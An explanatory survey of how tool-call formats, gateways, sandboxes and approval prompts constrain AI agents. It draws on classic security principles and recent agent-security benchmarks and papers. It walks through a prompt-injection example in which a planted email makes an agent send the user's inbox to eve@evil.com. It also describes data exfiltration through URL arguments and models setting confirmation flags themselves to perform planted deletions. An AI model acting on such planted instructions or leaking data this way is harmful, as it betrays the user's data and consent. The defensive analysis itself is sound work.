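# Mediating interfaces and action limits between AI agents and external tools

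## What stands between an agent and its tools

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop. The model chooses an action, receives the result, and chooses again until the task is done. The model produces only text, so another program has to read that text and carry out actions such as sending an email or changing a file. The model requests an action with a tool call, which is structured text that gives a tool's name and its arguments. A mediating layer is any software between the model and the outside resource that can pass, change, delay or refuse the request. Examples include tool-call formats, policy checkers, gateways, sandboxes and approval prompts.

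Such layers matter because agents spend much of their time reading text written by strangers (web pages, incoming mail, other people's code), and some of it is written to manipulate the agent. Agents also make mistakes. Security engineers have dealt with untrusted programs for more than fifty years, and one of their oldest methods is to give the program a closed list of permitted actions, fixed before it starts. It is an open question whether such a list can constrain an AI agent and still let it do its job. The answer depends largely on where the list is enforced and what information is available at that point.

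### The loop, one step at a time

Anthropic's *How tool use works*, part of the developer documentation for the Claude models, describes the cycle in five steps. The application sends the model the user's message and a list of available tools. The model replies with one or more tool calls, each consisting of a name and a set of arguments in JSON, a plain-text format for structured data. The application runs the operation. It then sends the model the whole conversation so far, plus the result, in a new request. The cycle repeats until the model replies without a tool call. OpenAI's *Function calling* describes essentially the same flow for the GPT models. In both cases the model only writes requests, which the application's code may or may not carry out.

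Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, a system that restricts agents' tool calls, reduce the loop to two lines. Write A for the agent, E for the environment in which the tools run, and o₀ for the user's request. At step i:

cᵢ = A(oᵢ₋₁)

oᵢ = E(cᵢ)

The loop ends when cᵢ is a final answer instead of a tool call, or when it reaches a step limit. A mediating layer goes between the two lines. If it allows the call, oᵢ is the tool's output. If it refuses, oᵢ is an error message, which the agent reads like any other result, and the run continues. The agent may then find a harmless alternative, abandon the task, or try the same thing with a different tool.

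Even the simplest agent has some mediation built in. In OpenAI's sample code, the definition of a weather tool specifies that `location` is text and that `units` is either celsius or fahrenheit. The dispatcher, the code that matches each call to the function that carries it out, raises an error if the call names an undefined tool.

Where a tool runs affects who can check its calls. Most tools run in the developer's own application, which receives each call before acting on it. For a few others, including web search, page fetching and code execution, Anthropic runs the operation on its own servers and usually returns the result to the model before the application receives a response. In those cases, a checker inside the application cannot stop a page fetch, because it has already happened. The developer can leave the tool switched off or rely on whatever checks Anthropic has.

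### An inbox and a planted instruction

The running example in *Progent* is small enough to keep in one's head. A user asks an assistant to carry out the actions listed in an email from alice@gmail.com with the subject "TODOs for the week". The assistant has tools for mail and for the chat service Slack, and the run goes like this:

1. `search_emails`, with that sender and subject, returns the to-do list: summarize the recent mail and post the summary to the user's Slack.
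2. `get_slack_info` returns the user's Slack handle, `alice`.
3. `read_emails(recent=20)` returns twenty messages. One of them contains an instruction to forward the inbox to eve@evil.com.
4. `send_email(to=eve@evil.com)`, with the inbox as the body, sends the user's mail to a stranger.
5. `send_slack_msg(to=alice)` posts the summary.

The user gets the summary and may never notice step 4. This is prompt injection, in which text planted in material the agent reads makes it follow someone else's instructions. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) traces the weakness to language models working directly on text, with no formal way to tell instructions from data.

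A rule that the agent must never obey instructions found in an email would have stopped the task at step 1, because the to-do list the user wanted it to follow was itself a set of instructions in an email. For Shi and colleagues, the central problem is that the legitimate request for more tools and the malicious one reach the agent through the same channel, as tool results that change its plan.

*Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (2026) reports that Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Sonnet 4.6 held back after detecting a forged claim, while certain other models called the claim forged and acted on it anyway. In a fully logged re-run, 25 of 509 executions (about 5%) came with such a statement in the same response, so a model's stated suspicion is not a reliable safeguard. None of the prompt-based defences in the study worked across all the models. The paper concludes that, for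 models that act while voicing doubt, enforcement has to move outside the context window, the text that the model reads.

### Where a check can sit

Controls can be placed at several points outside the context window. The table traces the malicious call from step 4 on its way to the mail service.

| Point | What it sees of step 4 | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Call format | Two fields, `to` and `body`, with their declared types | Whether this recipient has anything to do with the task |
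| Dispatcher | The tool's name, both arguments and, if the application supplies it, the user's request | Whatever a tool does once it has started |
| Gateway (a server that many agents share to reach many tools) | The same call, plus the identity of the agent and its user | Tools that the agent reaches by another route |
| Operating system | Processes, files and network connections | Why the agent wants them |
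| Network | The destination and, if a proxy can decrypt the traffic, the content | Changes to local files |
| The mail service itself | A valid request from the user's own account | That a stranger's text prompted it |

Shi and colleagues put their checker at the tool call, arguing that every outside effect of an agent passes through one and that a name with typed arguments is far easier to check than free text. This reasoning holds for the inbox assistant but is harder to defend once one of the tools runs shell commands. Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026), whose system *KAIROS* checks an agent's effects at the edge of a virtual machine, object that a checker at the tool interface covers only the actions an agent declares, so it misses what a script does when the agent writes and then runs one. *Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection* (2026) likewise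 objects that AgentSpec, a rule checker for tool calls, does not monitor the system calls (a program's requests to the operating system) that the tools make.

Moving the check down to the operating system closes that gap, because the kernel observes exactly what a process does. But it observes only low-level events, such as files opening and bytes leaving, and these don't show that an agent is, for example, forwarding the inbox to a stranger. The kernel-layer paper describes Argus, a system that first captures the user's intended task and then has to match low-level events against it. The paper acknowledges a semantic gap between the two.

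A designer can also use two points together. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (2026) combines a best-effort filter on tool calls with a stricter layer underneath, such as an HTTP proxy or a typed wrapper around the tool. The paper's proofs cover only the lower layer. The design keeps the filter because it can catch suspicious arguments early and add context, though the paper gives no detection rates for it.

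### Ideas from before language models

Most of the vocabulary for all this dates from the 1970s, when the untrusted party was another user of the same mainframe. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, reported to the US Air Force on how people with different security clearances could share one machine. The threat that worried his panel was a malicious user with legitimate access who could write and run arbitrary programs. Keeping outsiders out does nothing against somebody who is already in. The panel's answer was the reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every reference a program makes to other programs, data or devices against a list of what that user may do. It has three requirements:

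- It must be tamper-proof, since a checker that the attacker can alter protects nothing.
- The system must invoke it every time. If some programs run with the check suspended, then those programs are part of the security mechanism and have to meet the other two requirements themselves.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, or else nobody has grounds for believing that it works.

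Anderson applied the requirements to the Honeywell 635, a machine then in use, and its GCOS III operating system. The hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory. But programs called the supervisor for input and output, and the supervisor mostly ran with that memory check turned off, so the system failed the second requirement. Treating the supervisor itself as the monitor would fail the third, because the supervisor and its supporting software ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions.

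Anyone who builds a checker for agents from another language model can make the same mistake, because nobody can test that model completely either. Hempel and colleagues use a language model to rule on doubtful cases, but they keep it outside the part of the system that their confinement guarantees depend on.

A year after the Air Force report, Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, asked how a customer can run a borrowed program on private data and be sure that the program does not pass the data to its owner. The simplest leaks he listed are writing to a file in the owner's directory and sending a message to one of the owner's processes. The program can also encode information in the bill for its services, or open and close files so that another process can read bits from the system's locks. It can also vary how much it computes and reads from disk, so that an accomplice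 can get information from changes in the machine's speed. Lampson called routes of this last sort, which nobody intended for passing information, covert channels.

Forbidding a confined program to call any other program would stop all of these leaks, but Lampson called this rule "quite impractical" and spent the rest of the note on weaker ones. Under those, a confined program may call other programs if they are confined too or if the customer trusts them. The trusted supervisor then has to find every channel and block it or, if the customer will tolerate some leakage, limit how much it can carry. Agents present the same difficulty, because the inbox assistant must be able to post a summary, which can carry a secret about as well as a bill can.

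Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* collected the field's design principles in 1975. Complete mediation, their rule that the system must check every access to every object, restates Anderson's second requirement. Least privilege is the principle that each program and user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". Their first reason for it was to limit damage from accident or error, ahead of deliberate misuse. Under their principle of fail-safe defaults, a system lists what is permitted instead of what is forbidden, because mistakes are then easier to notice. An error in a list of permissions tends to block something legitimate, so someone soon complains, whereas an error in a list of prohibitions tends to let something through unnoticed. For example, a rule that bans eve@evil.com no longer stops Eve once she opens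 a new account.

Least privilege has become the standard advice for agents. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) recommends that an agent's permissions fit its current task and change as the task evolves, with explicit reauthorization for anything beyond them. The inbox example shows why permissions need to change and why this is hard to do. The assistant needs only one tool before step 1, and nobody can say which others it will need until it has read the email. Some permissions, such as permission to click, are also hard to scope. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) says that fine-grained rules suit agents whose tools have well-defined meanings, but not agents that operate a browser, a desktop or a phone.

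The last of the older ideas explains how an attack can succeed without anyone breaking a rule. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a "nearly true story" from the timesharing company Tymshare. A compiler kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the operators gave it permission to write in that directory. Users could also tell the compiler where to put its debugging output. One user gave it the name of the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the billing information was lost.

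The compiler's code had been correct when its programmers wrote it. Hardy concluded that the compiler held authority from two sources, its operators and whoever was running it, and had no way to specify which to use for a given file. A confused deputy is a program with legitimate rights that somebody leads into misusing them. Step 4 fits this description closely because the agent uses the user's right to send mail with an address supplied by Eve.

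These principles can still be used to classify current failures reasonably well. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) maps attacks on real AI products to the principles they violate. It lists exposed network ports in the coding agent Devin under least privilege and secure information flow, and an account takeover at DeepSeek under complete mediation and secure information flow.

### Confinement and authorization

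Hempel and colleagues draw a distinction that clears up a good deal of confusion about what any given layer achieves. Confinement is the guarantee that no effect of the agent reaches the outside except through the mediating layer. Authorization is the decision about which of the effects that arrive there may go through. (This is a more modest notion of confinement than Lampson's. He wanted no leaks at all, whereas here the promise is a single exit with a guard on it, and *KAIROS* sets covert channels aside.)

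Neither confinement nor authorization is enough alone to stop the message to Eve. The inbox assistant could run in a perfect sandbox, an isolated environment whose only exit leads past a monitor, and the message would still go out if the monitor's rules let the assistant send mail. The dispatcher could instead hold a flawless rule about who may receive email. But if the assistant can also run scripts with open network access, the injected instruction can ask for a script that sends the message without the dispatcher checking that rule.

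The confinement in *KAIROS* holds even against an entirely hostile agent, provided that the host is trustworthy and the list of channels out is complete. Hempel and colleagues offer no such guarantee for authorization, because it depends on a statement of what the user wants, and users rarely give a full one beforehand. They assume that an injected agent does not deliberately disguise the data it handles, and they measure how often the authorization decisions are correct.

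### Why safety and usefulness pull apart

The access that makes an agent useful also allows attackers or the agent's own mistakes to cause harm. If the inbox assistant has only `search_emails`, it can't carry out the theft, but it can't complete its task either. With every mail and Slack tool, it can do both. Even without an attacker, an assistant that is allowed to post can misread the to-do list and post a private summary to the wrong person.

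In the inbox example, a policy that allowed only reading mail and posting to one Slack handle would have stopped Eve without interfering with the job, which never required sending an email. But somebody has to write that policy partway through the run, once the to-do list and the handle are known, and it is wrong for the next task, which may well be to email Alice an update. Shi and colleagues point out that a policy loose enough for every task is too broad to block attacks, while a policy made for one task is too narrow for any other. Asking the user to approve each call would solve this problem but remove most of the reason for having an agent.

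Other tasks have no good solution even in hindsight. One task in *AgentDojo* is to invite Dora to Slack using the email address on her website, which the user does not control. A layer that refuses to act on addresses from untrusted pages prevents the agent from completing the task, but accepting them lets anyone who can edit the page choose who is invited. Strictness can also make an agent much less useful. When Hempel and colleagues had *KAIROS* refuse everything it could not approve under its written policy, the agent finished only 42.7% of ordinary tasks, about half as many as it finished without the defense.

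### Measuring both at once

Any claim about a mediating layer needs at least two numbers. The attack success rate is the share of planted attacks in which the agent carries out the attacker's goal. Utility is the share of the user's own tasks that the agent completes, and researchers report it both without attacks (benign utility) and with them (utility under attack). Neither figure means much alone, because a layer can reach an attack success rate of zero by refusing every call.

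Most of the published figures come from AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and colleagues built at ETH Zurich and the company Invariant Labs. It simulates four applications, each with its own data (an inbox, a calendar, bank transactions) and tools that read and change the data. A user task is a request in plain language plus code that determines whether the agent solved it by inspecting the agent's answer and the state of the application before and after. An injection task is an attacker's goal with a similar check. The application data contain placeholders for the attacker's text, for example in the body of an email. AgentDojo uses fixed code rather than a language model as the judge because text that hijacks the agent might also hijack the judge.

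Within each suite, every user task meets every injection task, which gives 97 user tasks and 629 injection cases:

| Suite | Tools | User tasks | Injection tasks | Injection cases |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (mail, calendar, files) | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 74 | 97 | 27 | 629 |

Some tasks require a chain of up to 18 tool calls. The attacker's goals range from sending a phishing link to transferring as much money as possible. Most papers use a generic attack message telling the agent that it must do the attacker's task before the user's.

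The 629 cases contain only 27 distinct goals, so a defence that blocks a single Workspace goal improves the results in 40 cases. Debenedetti and colleagues also found that more capable models tended to be easier to attack, perhaps because weaker models often fail at the attacker's task even when they fall for the injection. An attack success rate is therefore best compared with the same model's rate with no defence.

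The benchmark has also grown. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts more than 900 combinations. Part of the increase probably comes from *agentdojo inspect*, a US government version that added Workspace attacks for stealing data in bulk. The main project has since adopted those attacks. Hempel and colleagues still report on 629 combinations, so two AgentDojo results may not cover the same attacks.

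The definition of utility under attack also varies slightly between papers. Debenedetti and colleagues count a case only if the agent solves the user's task without adversarial side effects, while Hempel and colleagues measure the share of user tasks completed in the injection cases. The inbox run, in which the agent delivers the summary but also leaks the mail, fails under the first definition and passes under the second.

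AgentDojo is also limited as a test of layers that work below the tool call, because its tools are simulated objects in the memory of a single program, with no operating system or network boundary for such a layer to guard. To test *KAIROS* on it, Hempel and colleagues had to write an adapter that turns each simulated call into the kind of event their monitor can process. The resulting scores are evidence about the monitor's decisions, but not about whether the virtual machine would contain a real agent.

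## Fixed lists of tools and what they rule out

The simplest way to limit an agent is to give it a list of tools and refuse everything else. Many applications now get such lists through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data. Its current revision took effect on 28 July 2026. By then, according to Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026), developers were downloading MCP's software kits more than 400 million times a month.

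### A tool call in MCP

Three pieces of software take part. The host is the application the user works in, such as a chat program or a coding assistant. The server offers tools and carries them out, either on the user's own machine or somewhere on the internet. A client inside the host passes messages between the two. Under Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the specification that covers tools, a call goes like this:

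1. The client sends the request `tools/list`. The server replies with a definition of each tool and the length of time for which the client may reuse the reply.
2. The host gives the definitions to the model, which writes a call.
3. The client sends the server a `tools/call` request containing the tool's name and the arguments.
4. The server checks the arguments, runs its own code and returns a result, which can be text, images or structured data. It can also ask for something first, such as an answer from the user.

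The inbox assistant's mail tool would have a definition along these lines:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Send an email from the user's account",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "to": { "type": "string" },
      "body": { "type": "string" }
    },
    "required": ["to", "body"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

The input schema uses JSON Schema, a standard language for describing the shape of JSON data. This one requires two text fields, and its last line forbids any others, which would otherwise be allowed. A much stricter schema could, for example, limit `to` to a few named addresses or cap the length of `body`. The July revision allowed input schemas to use every keyword in the 2020 version of JSON Schema, including those for conditional rules.

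The server supplies the schema, so the host can't fully trust it either. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) forbids software from automatically fetching missing parts of a schema from the network. It also recommends limiting a schema's depth and the time spent checking it, because a malicious schema could tie up the program that checks it.

A mistaken tool call produces one of two kinds of error. A call to a tool that isn't on the list gets a protocol error, which the client may or may not show the model. A call with a bad value, such as a departure date in the past, gets an ordinary result marked as an error. The client should pass this result to the model so that the model can correct the call and try again.

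The specification requires servers to validate all inputs, but the protocol cannot enforce this. The schemas themselves are at least well formed. Afsar (2026), in *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, drew 400 locally installed servers at random from the official registry and tried to start each one. Only 195 started and answered, but none of their 2,766 tools had a fatal schema error. The test did not run any tool that changes things, so it is evidence about the definitions and not about how strictly servers enforce them.

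### Well-formed calls that still do harm

Model providers can stop a malformed call even earlier. A model writes one token (a word or a fragment of one) at a time, and at each step it gives every token t in its vocabulary a probability p(t). In constrained decoding, the software that runs the model follows the schema as the text grows and works out the set V of tokens that could still lead to a valid call. It then sets every other token's probability to zero and rescales the rest:

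p′(t) = p(t) / Σₛ∈V p(s) if t is in V, and p′(t) = 0 otherwise

With the weather tool in OpenAI's sample code, once the model has written `"units": "`, the next token must begin "celsius" or "fahrenheit". The call can be malformed only if the output reaches its length limit partway through. An MCP server cannot detect whether the client's model was constrained this way, so it still has to check the arguments.

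The rescaling can make the model choose a permitted but wrong value. Suppose the schema limits `to` to eight approved addresses and the user asks for a message to Dora, who is not among them. Once the model has started the call, it must finish with one of the eight, even if it had given all of them tiny probabilities. It may therefore write to the wrong person, whereas an unconstrained model would have written Dora's address and received an error.

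More importantly, the schema restricts only the form of a call, so the message to Eve in the inbox example satisfies the definition above.

Some server authors require a field such as `confirm` to be true before a destructive tool will run, but the server can't distinguish a value the model filled in from a person's consent. *When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) tested this kind of field with a small server for deleting notes. The researchers planted an instruction to delete a second note that the user had never mentioned. In one condition, the planted text did not name the flag, but the tool's schema and refusal message did. The models tried the planted deletion 169 times and succeeded 127 times by setting the flag themselves.

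### What a closed list guarantees

Write T for the set of listed tools and Aₜ for the arguments that tool t accepts. Everything the agent can bring about through the list is then

effects(T) = ⋃ₜ∈T { effect(t, a) : a ∈ Aₜ }

The agent cannot use the listed tools to do anything outside this set. If no listed tool can delete a file, whatever arguments it is given, the agent cannot delete a file, even if an attacker has taken complete control of the model's instructions. A defence that depends on the model's judgement cannot provide this guarantee. A fixed list provides it only under certain conditions, which real deployments often fail to meet.

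Confinement has to hold, so that every route to the outside runs through the list. (A listed tool that runs code can break this condition from inside the list, and the next section takes that up.)

Each tool also has to do only what its definition declares. The host receives a name, a description and a schema, but someone else controls the code behind them and can write it badly or lie about what it does. A hostile server can also plant instructions in the description, which the model reads.

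MCP lets a server change its list of tools at any time, and the server can notify clients that request notice of changes. Since the July revision, the list may no longer differ between connections or change as a side effect of another request, though it may still depend on the user's permissions. To keep the interface strictly fixed, a host has to save a list that someone has approved and refuse later additions.

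The lists are mostly short. Afsar found a median of eight tools per server, though one server offered 300. But users often connect several servers at once, and even eight tools can allow a wide range of effects if their arguments are loosely restricted.

### Counting what an argument can carry

An argument with N possible values can carry at most log₂ N bits of information in each call. That makes it possible to compare fields that look equally harmless in a schema:

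| Argument | Possible values | Bits per call, at most |
|---|---|---|
| A yes/no flag | 2 | 1 |
| A recipient from eight approved names | 8 | 3 |
| A date within one year | 365 | about 8.5 |
| 100 free characters in a web address | 64¹⁰⁰ | 600 |

The last row assumes an alphabet of 64 symbols (upper- and lower-case letters, digits and two punctuation marks), which gives six bits per character. A sixteen-digit card number takes about 53 bits, so a single web address can hold eleven card numbers. Sending one through the recipient field would take eighteen calls, and Eve would have to find out who received each message.

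A tool that only reads web pages can still send data out through the addresses it requests. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that the website receives the full address and commonly records it. The user may never notice the request, because it can happen in the background, such as when the application loads an image.

The count has two limits. It applies to one field at a time, so restricting `to` to eight names leaves the body of the email free, and the restriction protects only as far as those eight people can be trusted. The count also measures leakage, not damage. A one-bit flag on a deletion tool can be enough to delete a database.

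Designers of web-reading tools have tried several ways to reduce the number of possible addresses. A length limit does little, since Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* accepts addresses of up to 250 characters, which by the same arithmetic can hold nearly 1,500 bits. The stronger rule is that the model can fetch only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, for example in the user's message or in search results. This leaves perhaps a few dozen choices, but choosing among them still conveys information. In July, Willison (2026), a developer who writes about AI security, described how a researcher had extracted personal details through the model's choice of links on a hostile page, a route that Anthropic has since closed.

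OpenAI gives two reasons why a list of trusted websites is not enough for ChatGPT. First, many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a request can start on an approved site and end on an attacker's. Second, strict lists produce so many false alarms that people learn to click through the warnings.

OpenAI instead checks whether the exact address the agent wants to load already appears in an index of public pages, which a crawler builds without access to anyone's conversations. If it does, the agent can load the page automatically, because an address that was already public is much less likely to contain the user's secrets. Otherwise, the system tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning. OpenAI claims only that this prevents quiet leaks through the address itself, and the page may still contain hostile instructions.

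### Four hints about what a tool does

Schemas describe arguments and are silent about consequences. For those, MCP has four optional annotations, each a yes/no field in the tool's definition. The maintainers of the Model Context Protocol describe them as follows:

| Annotation | Meaning when true | Assumed if missing | What a client might do |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool does not modify its environment | False | Skip the confirmation prompt |
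| `destructiveHint` | Its changes can destroy something, not just add to it | True | Warn the user first |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating the same call is safe | False | Retry after a failure |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside parties | True | Check the output for untrusted content |

By default, a tool with no annotations counts as one that writes, may destroy things, is unsafe to repeat and reaches the outside world. This caution applies Saltzer and Schroeder's fail-safe principle to missing information.

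The specification nevertheless calls all four hints, and tells clients to distrust them unless they trust the server. A server can label a tool read-only even if the tool deletes the user's files. During the original review, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked how a client could use a flag that it cannot trust. Another reviewer, Basil Hosmer, wanted clients to ignore annotations from untrusted servers. Under the compromise, each client decides how much weight to give the annotations. The maintainers now recommend relying on deterministic controls, such as network rules or a sandbox, for safety guarantees.

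An accurate label can still mislead. A tool that fetches web pages changes nothing, so its author can fairly mark it read-only. A client that skips the prompt for read-only tools will then let it send 600 bits to a stranger without asking the user. Of the four hints, only the open-world hint indicates this danger.

Many servers leave the hints out. Afsar found none on 58.8% of tools. Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, collected the definitions of 98,291 tools from remote servers and found at least one annotation on 74.0% of them. But a single publisher supplied 45% of the tools and filled in all four fields on every one, presumably from a template. Without that publisher, the share falls to 52.8%. Only 3.1% of all the tools are labeled as destructive.

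Hosts make little use of the labels they do get. Yao and colleagues examined the source code of 41 open-source hosts and developer kits and found that in 39 of them, marking a tool as destructive did not change whether the user was asked for approval. Some of these ask before every ordinary call, and the rest never ask. The researchers then paired each of 269 destructive tools with each of the 25 finished applications in the sample. In 60.7% of the pairs, the tool would run by default without human approval.

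If every application followed the cautious defaults and asked about any tool not labelled safe, that share would fall to 5.4%. Most of the remaining cases are destructive tools whose own annotations call them read-only or non-destructive. Users would also get many more unnecessary prompts. Among tools that the study's software flagged as destructive but that turned out to be harmless, the share of pairs in which the user gets a prompt would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%. A later section covers whether people still read prompts at that rate.

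Users could also shorten the list by hiding every tool that writes, but the maintainers know of no MCP client that lets people filter tools by annotation. The closest thing in production is GitHub's read-only mode, which about 17% of users enable. Some of the others surely need to write, and some may never have seen the setting.

### Risk in the combination of tools

The maintainers' deeper objection is that no label on a single tool can capture its risk. They borrow Willison's "lethal trifecta", three capabilities that together make data theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. An agent with all three can read an attacker's instruction, collect the private data and send it off, but the theft fails if any one of them is missing.

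By this reasoning, whether `search_emails` is safe depends on what else the agent can use. The inbox assistant has the whole trifecta because the mail is private, strangers wrote some of it, and two of the tools send messages. Removing `send_email` would leave the trifecta intact if `send_slack_msg` accepts any recipient.

MCP makes it easy to assemble such combinations by accident. A user might connect a calendar server one day and a tool that runs code the next, and neither server's author knows about the other. Researchers have demonstrated an attack on this pair that starts with a malicious event description. The maintainers conclude that risk depends on all the tools available to the agent in a session. Checking each definition as it arrives will miss this risk. The whole set needs checking, and the host is the natural place to do it because the tools come together there. Several proposed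 annotations would help, for example by marking tools that return sensitive or untrusted data. A host could then apply stricter approval rules after such a tool has run.

Combinations can also go wrong without an attacker. Trofimov and Novikov describe an agent that books a trip on a budget of 1,500 euros. To save time, it books a flight for 900 euros and a hotel for 700 in parallel. Both calls use permitted tools with valid arguments, and both succeed, but together they exceed the budget. The agent cancels the hotel and is left with a non-refundable flight. In another of their examples, an agent pays an invoice, receives no acknowledgment and pays again.

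In the second case, the agent can learn from the idempotent hint not to repeat a payment, but it can't learn whether the first payment went through. None of the four hints covers the first case, where the limit applies to the sum of two calls. A mediating layer could enforce the budget only by keeping a running total across calls.

### From WebGPT to Lockdown Mode

A fixed list worked well for one of the first language models that could use the web. In *WebGPT*, Nakano, Hilton and colleagues (2021) trained OpenAI's GPT-3 to answer questions using a text-only browser that accepted ten commands. The model could search with Bing, follow a link, find text on the page, save a quotation, scroll up or down, jump to the top, go back, and end the session in one of two ways. Any other text had no effect but still counted as an action, and the model could take at most 100 actions in the evaluations.

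The system was useful despite its fixed list of tools. Human judges preferred the best model's answers to answers written by people using the same browser 56% of the time, and to the top-voted answers on Reddit 69% of the time.

Nakano and colleagues also noted that, with live web access, a model that could fill in forms might edit Wikipedia to create a reliable-looking reference for its own answer. If it happened to do this during training, reinforcement learning would probably reward it. They judged the risk from WebGPT very low because it could affect the outside world only by sending queries to Bing and following existing links. But they thought a capable enough system could find ways around these limits, and they argued that the burden of proving web access safe should grow with a model's abilities, even during training.

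WebGPT was also an easy case. By the arithmetic above, a free-text search query is a wide channel, but WebGPT's queries went to Bing rather than to an attacker, and the model held no private data worth stealing. Current agents often have access to mail, files and company records, and they do more than read. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (2026) cites Stein's analysis of 177,436 public MCP tools, in which tools that change something outside the agent rose from 27% to 65% of usage between November 2024 and February 2026.

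OpenAI now sells something closer to the old arrangement as an option. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced the setting in February for organizations, and OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts in June. In terms of the trifecta, Lockdown Mode leaves the private data and the untrusted content where they are and cuts down the communication with the outside. It does so with fixed restrictions that do not depend on the model's judgement. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the help article, lists what changes:

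- Web browsing uses only stored copies of pages, so search results can be out of date or missing.
- Deep research, which compiles long reports from many sources, and agent mode, which carries out tasks online, are both off.
- ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers and cannot fetch them from the web.
- It cannot download files for analysis, though it can still work on files that the user uploads.
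- Code that it writes in Canvas, its editing workspace, cannot use the network.
- On personal accounts, connected apps lose live access and the ability to write wherever these conflict with the protections. The shopping agents and the personal finance feature stop working.

These are some of the product's most useful features, and OpenAI says most people don't need the setting. The company only lists the features users lose and doesn't measure how many tasks they can no longer finish.

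The protection is also partial, as OpenAI acknowledges. A planted instruction can still arrive in a stored page or an uploaded file and distort the answer. In company workspaces, administrators choose which apps stay on, and each app may again let data leave. OpenAI advises them not to enable write actions, even in trusted apps, unless they can confirm that an attacker would not see the result. The setting also does not cover Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, which keeps whatever network access it had before.

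## When the permitted action is to run a program

Coding agents such as OpenAI's Codex do most of their work through a shell, the text interface in which programmers type commands. A shell is a single entry on a list of tools and takes one text argument, but it can start any program on the machine. Developers now also replace long lists of tools for calendars, office files and cloud services with a single tool that runs code, mainly to save money.

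### Why long lists are expensive

Developers pay for every token a model reads, including tool definitions and results. According to Anthropic, most MCP clients load all the definitions at the start, so an agent with thousands of tools may process hundreds of thousands of tokens before it reads the user's request. If a user asks an agent to copy a meeting transcript from Google Drive into a Salesforce record, the model reads the transcript as the result of one call and writes it out again as an argument of the next. For a two-hour meeting, that can add 50,000 tokens, and the model may make copying mistakes.

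Anthropic's alternative turns each tool into a function in its own file. The model opens only the files it needs and writes a short script that moves the transcript between the two services without passing it through the model. In the company's example, this cuts usage from 150,000 tokens to 2,000.

The internet infrastructure company Cloudflare went further. Carey's *Code Mode* describes an MCP server that uses two tools to cover all of the company's more than 2,500 endpoints, the addresses where other programs send requests to control its services. The `search` tool runs the model's JavaScript over a machine-readable description of the endpoints, and `execute` runs JavaScript that sends requests to them. The two tool definitions take about 1,000 tokens together, whereas defining a separate tool for every endpoint would take 1.17 million, more than the most advanced models could read at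 once.

Both figures come from companies describing their own systems, and both compare against the most wasteful alternative. A user who only wanted to manage domain names, for example, could already connect Cloudflare's smaller server for that product.

Savings over whole tasks are smaller. Mak, Suresh and colleagues (2026), in *Is Bash All You Need?*, gave two models a set of typed office tools, either as direct calls or as functions inside a script. The models used 48% and 57% fewer tokens with scripts than with direct calls on one benchmark, and 15% and 22% fewer on the other.

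Developers also expect models to be better at writing code than at making tool calls. *Codemode*, an older page of Cloudflare's documentation, explains that models have seen millions of lines of real code but only contrived tool calls. In *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026) tested this with 14 models on 309 tasks that required calling the right functions with the right arguments. Code matched or beat JSON calls for 11 of the models, often by only a few points. The other three scored 20 to 27 points lower with code because they wrote line breaks in a form that made their scripts fail.

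The advantage of scripts grew with the number of calls needed. Claude Sonnet 5 stopped making calls altogether when a request needed more than about 70 at once, while its scripts still made all 100 in the largest test. The functions in the study only returned their arguments, so the results don't show how well a script handles failures in a real service.

### Thirty-one calendar events

At a developers' event in 2025, Cloudflare's Rita Kozlov asked two agents to schedule a meetup at 5 p.m. every day in January 2026, each on a different topic. According to WorkOS's recap, *Cloudflare* (2025), one agent made more than thirty separate tool calls, and the other wrote code with a loop. Both created 31 events, but the agent that wrote code used 81% fewer tokens. For a single event, it used 32% fewer.

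The loop would look something like this, with the titles written out in full:

```js
const topics = [/* 31 titles */];
for (let day = 1; day <= 31; day++) {
  await calendar.create_event({
    title: topics[day - 1],
    start: `2026-01-${String(day).padStart(2, "0")}T17:00`
  });
}
```

What a checker can do with this job depends on how the agent submits it and where the checker sits:

| Arrangement | What reaches the checker | What it can decide |
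|---|---|---|
| Separate tool calls | 31 calls with their final arguments | Allow or refuse each event |
| Script, checked before it runs | One call to `execute`, with the script as text | Allow or refuse the whole script |
| Script, checked at each function call | 31 calls with their final arguments | Allow or refuse each event |
| Shell command with the calendar's password and open network access | One command | Allow or refuse the command; later traffic bypasses the checker |

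In the second row, the schema for `execute` requires only that the argument be text. A checker that reads the script won't find most of the dates, because the loop computes them. A person can easily see what this loop will do, but Rice's theorem shows that no procedure can correctly decide, for every program, whether it will ever do some particular thing.

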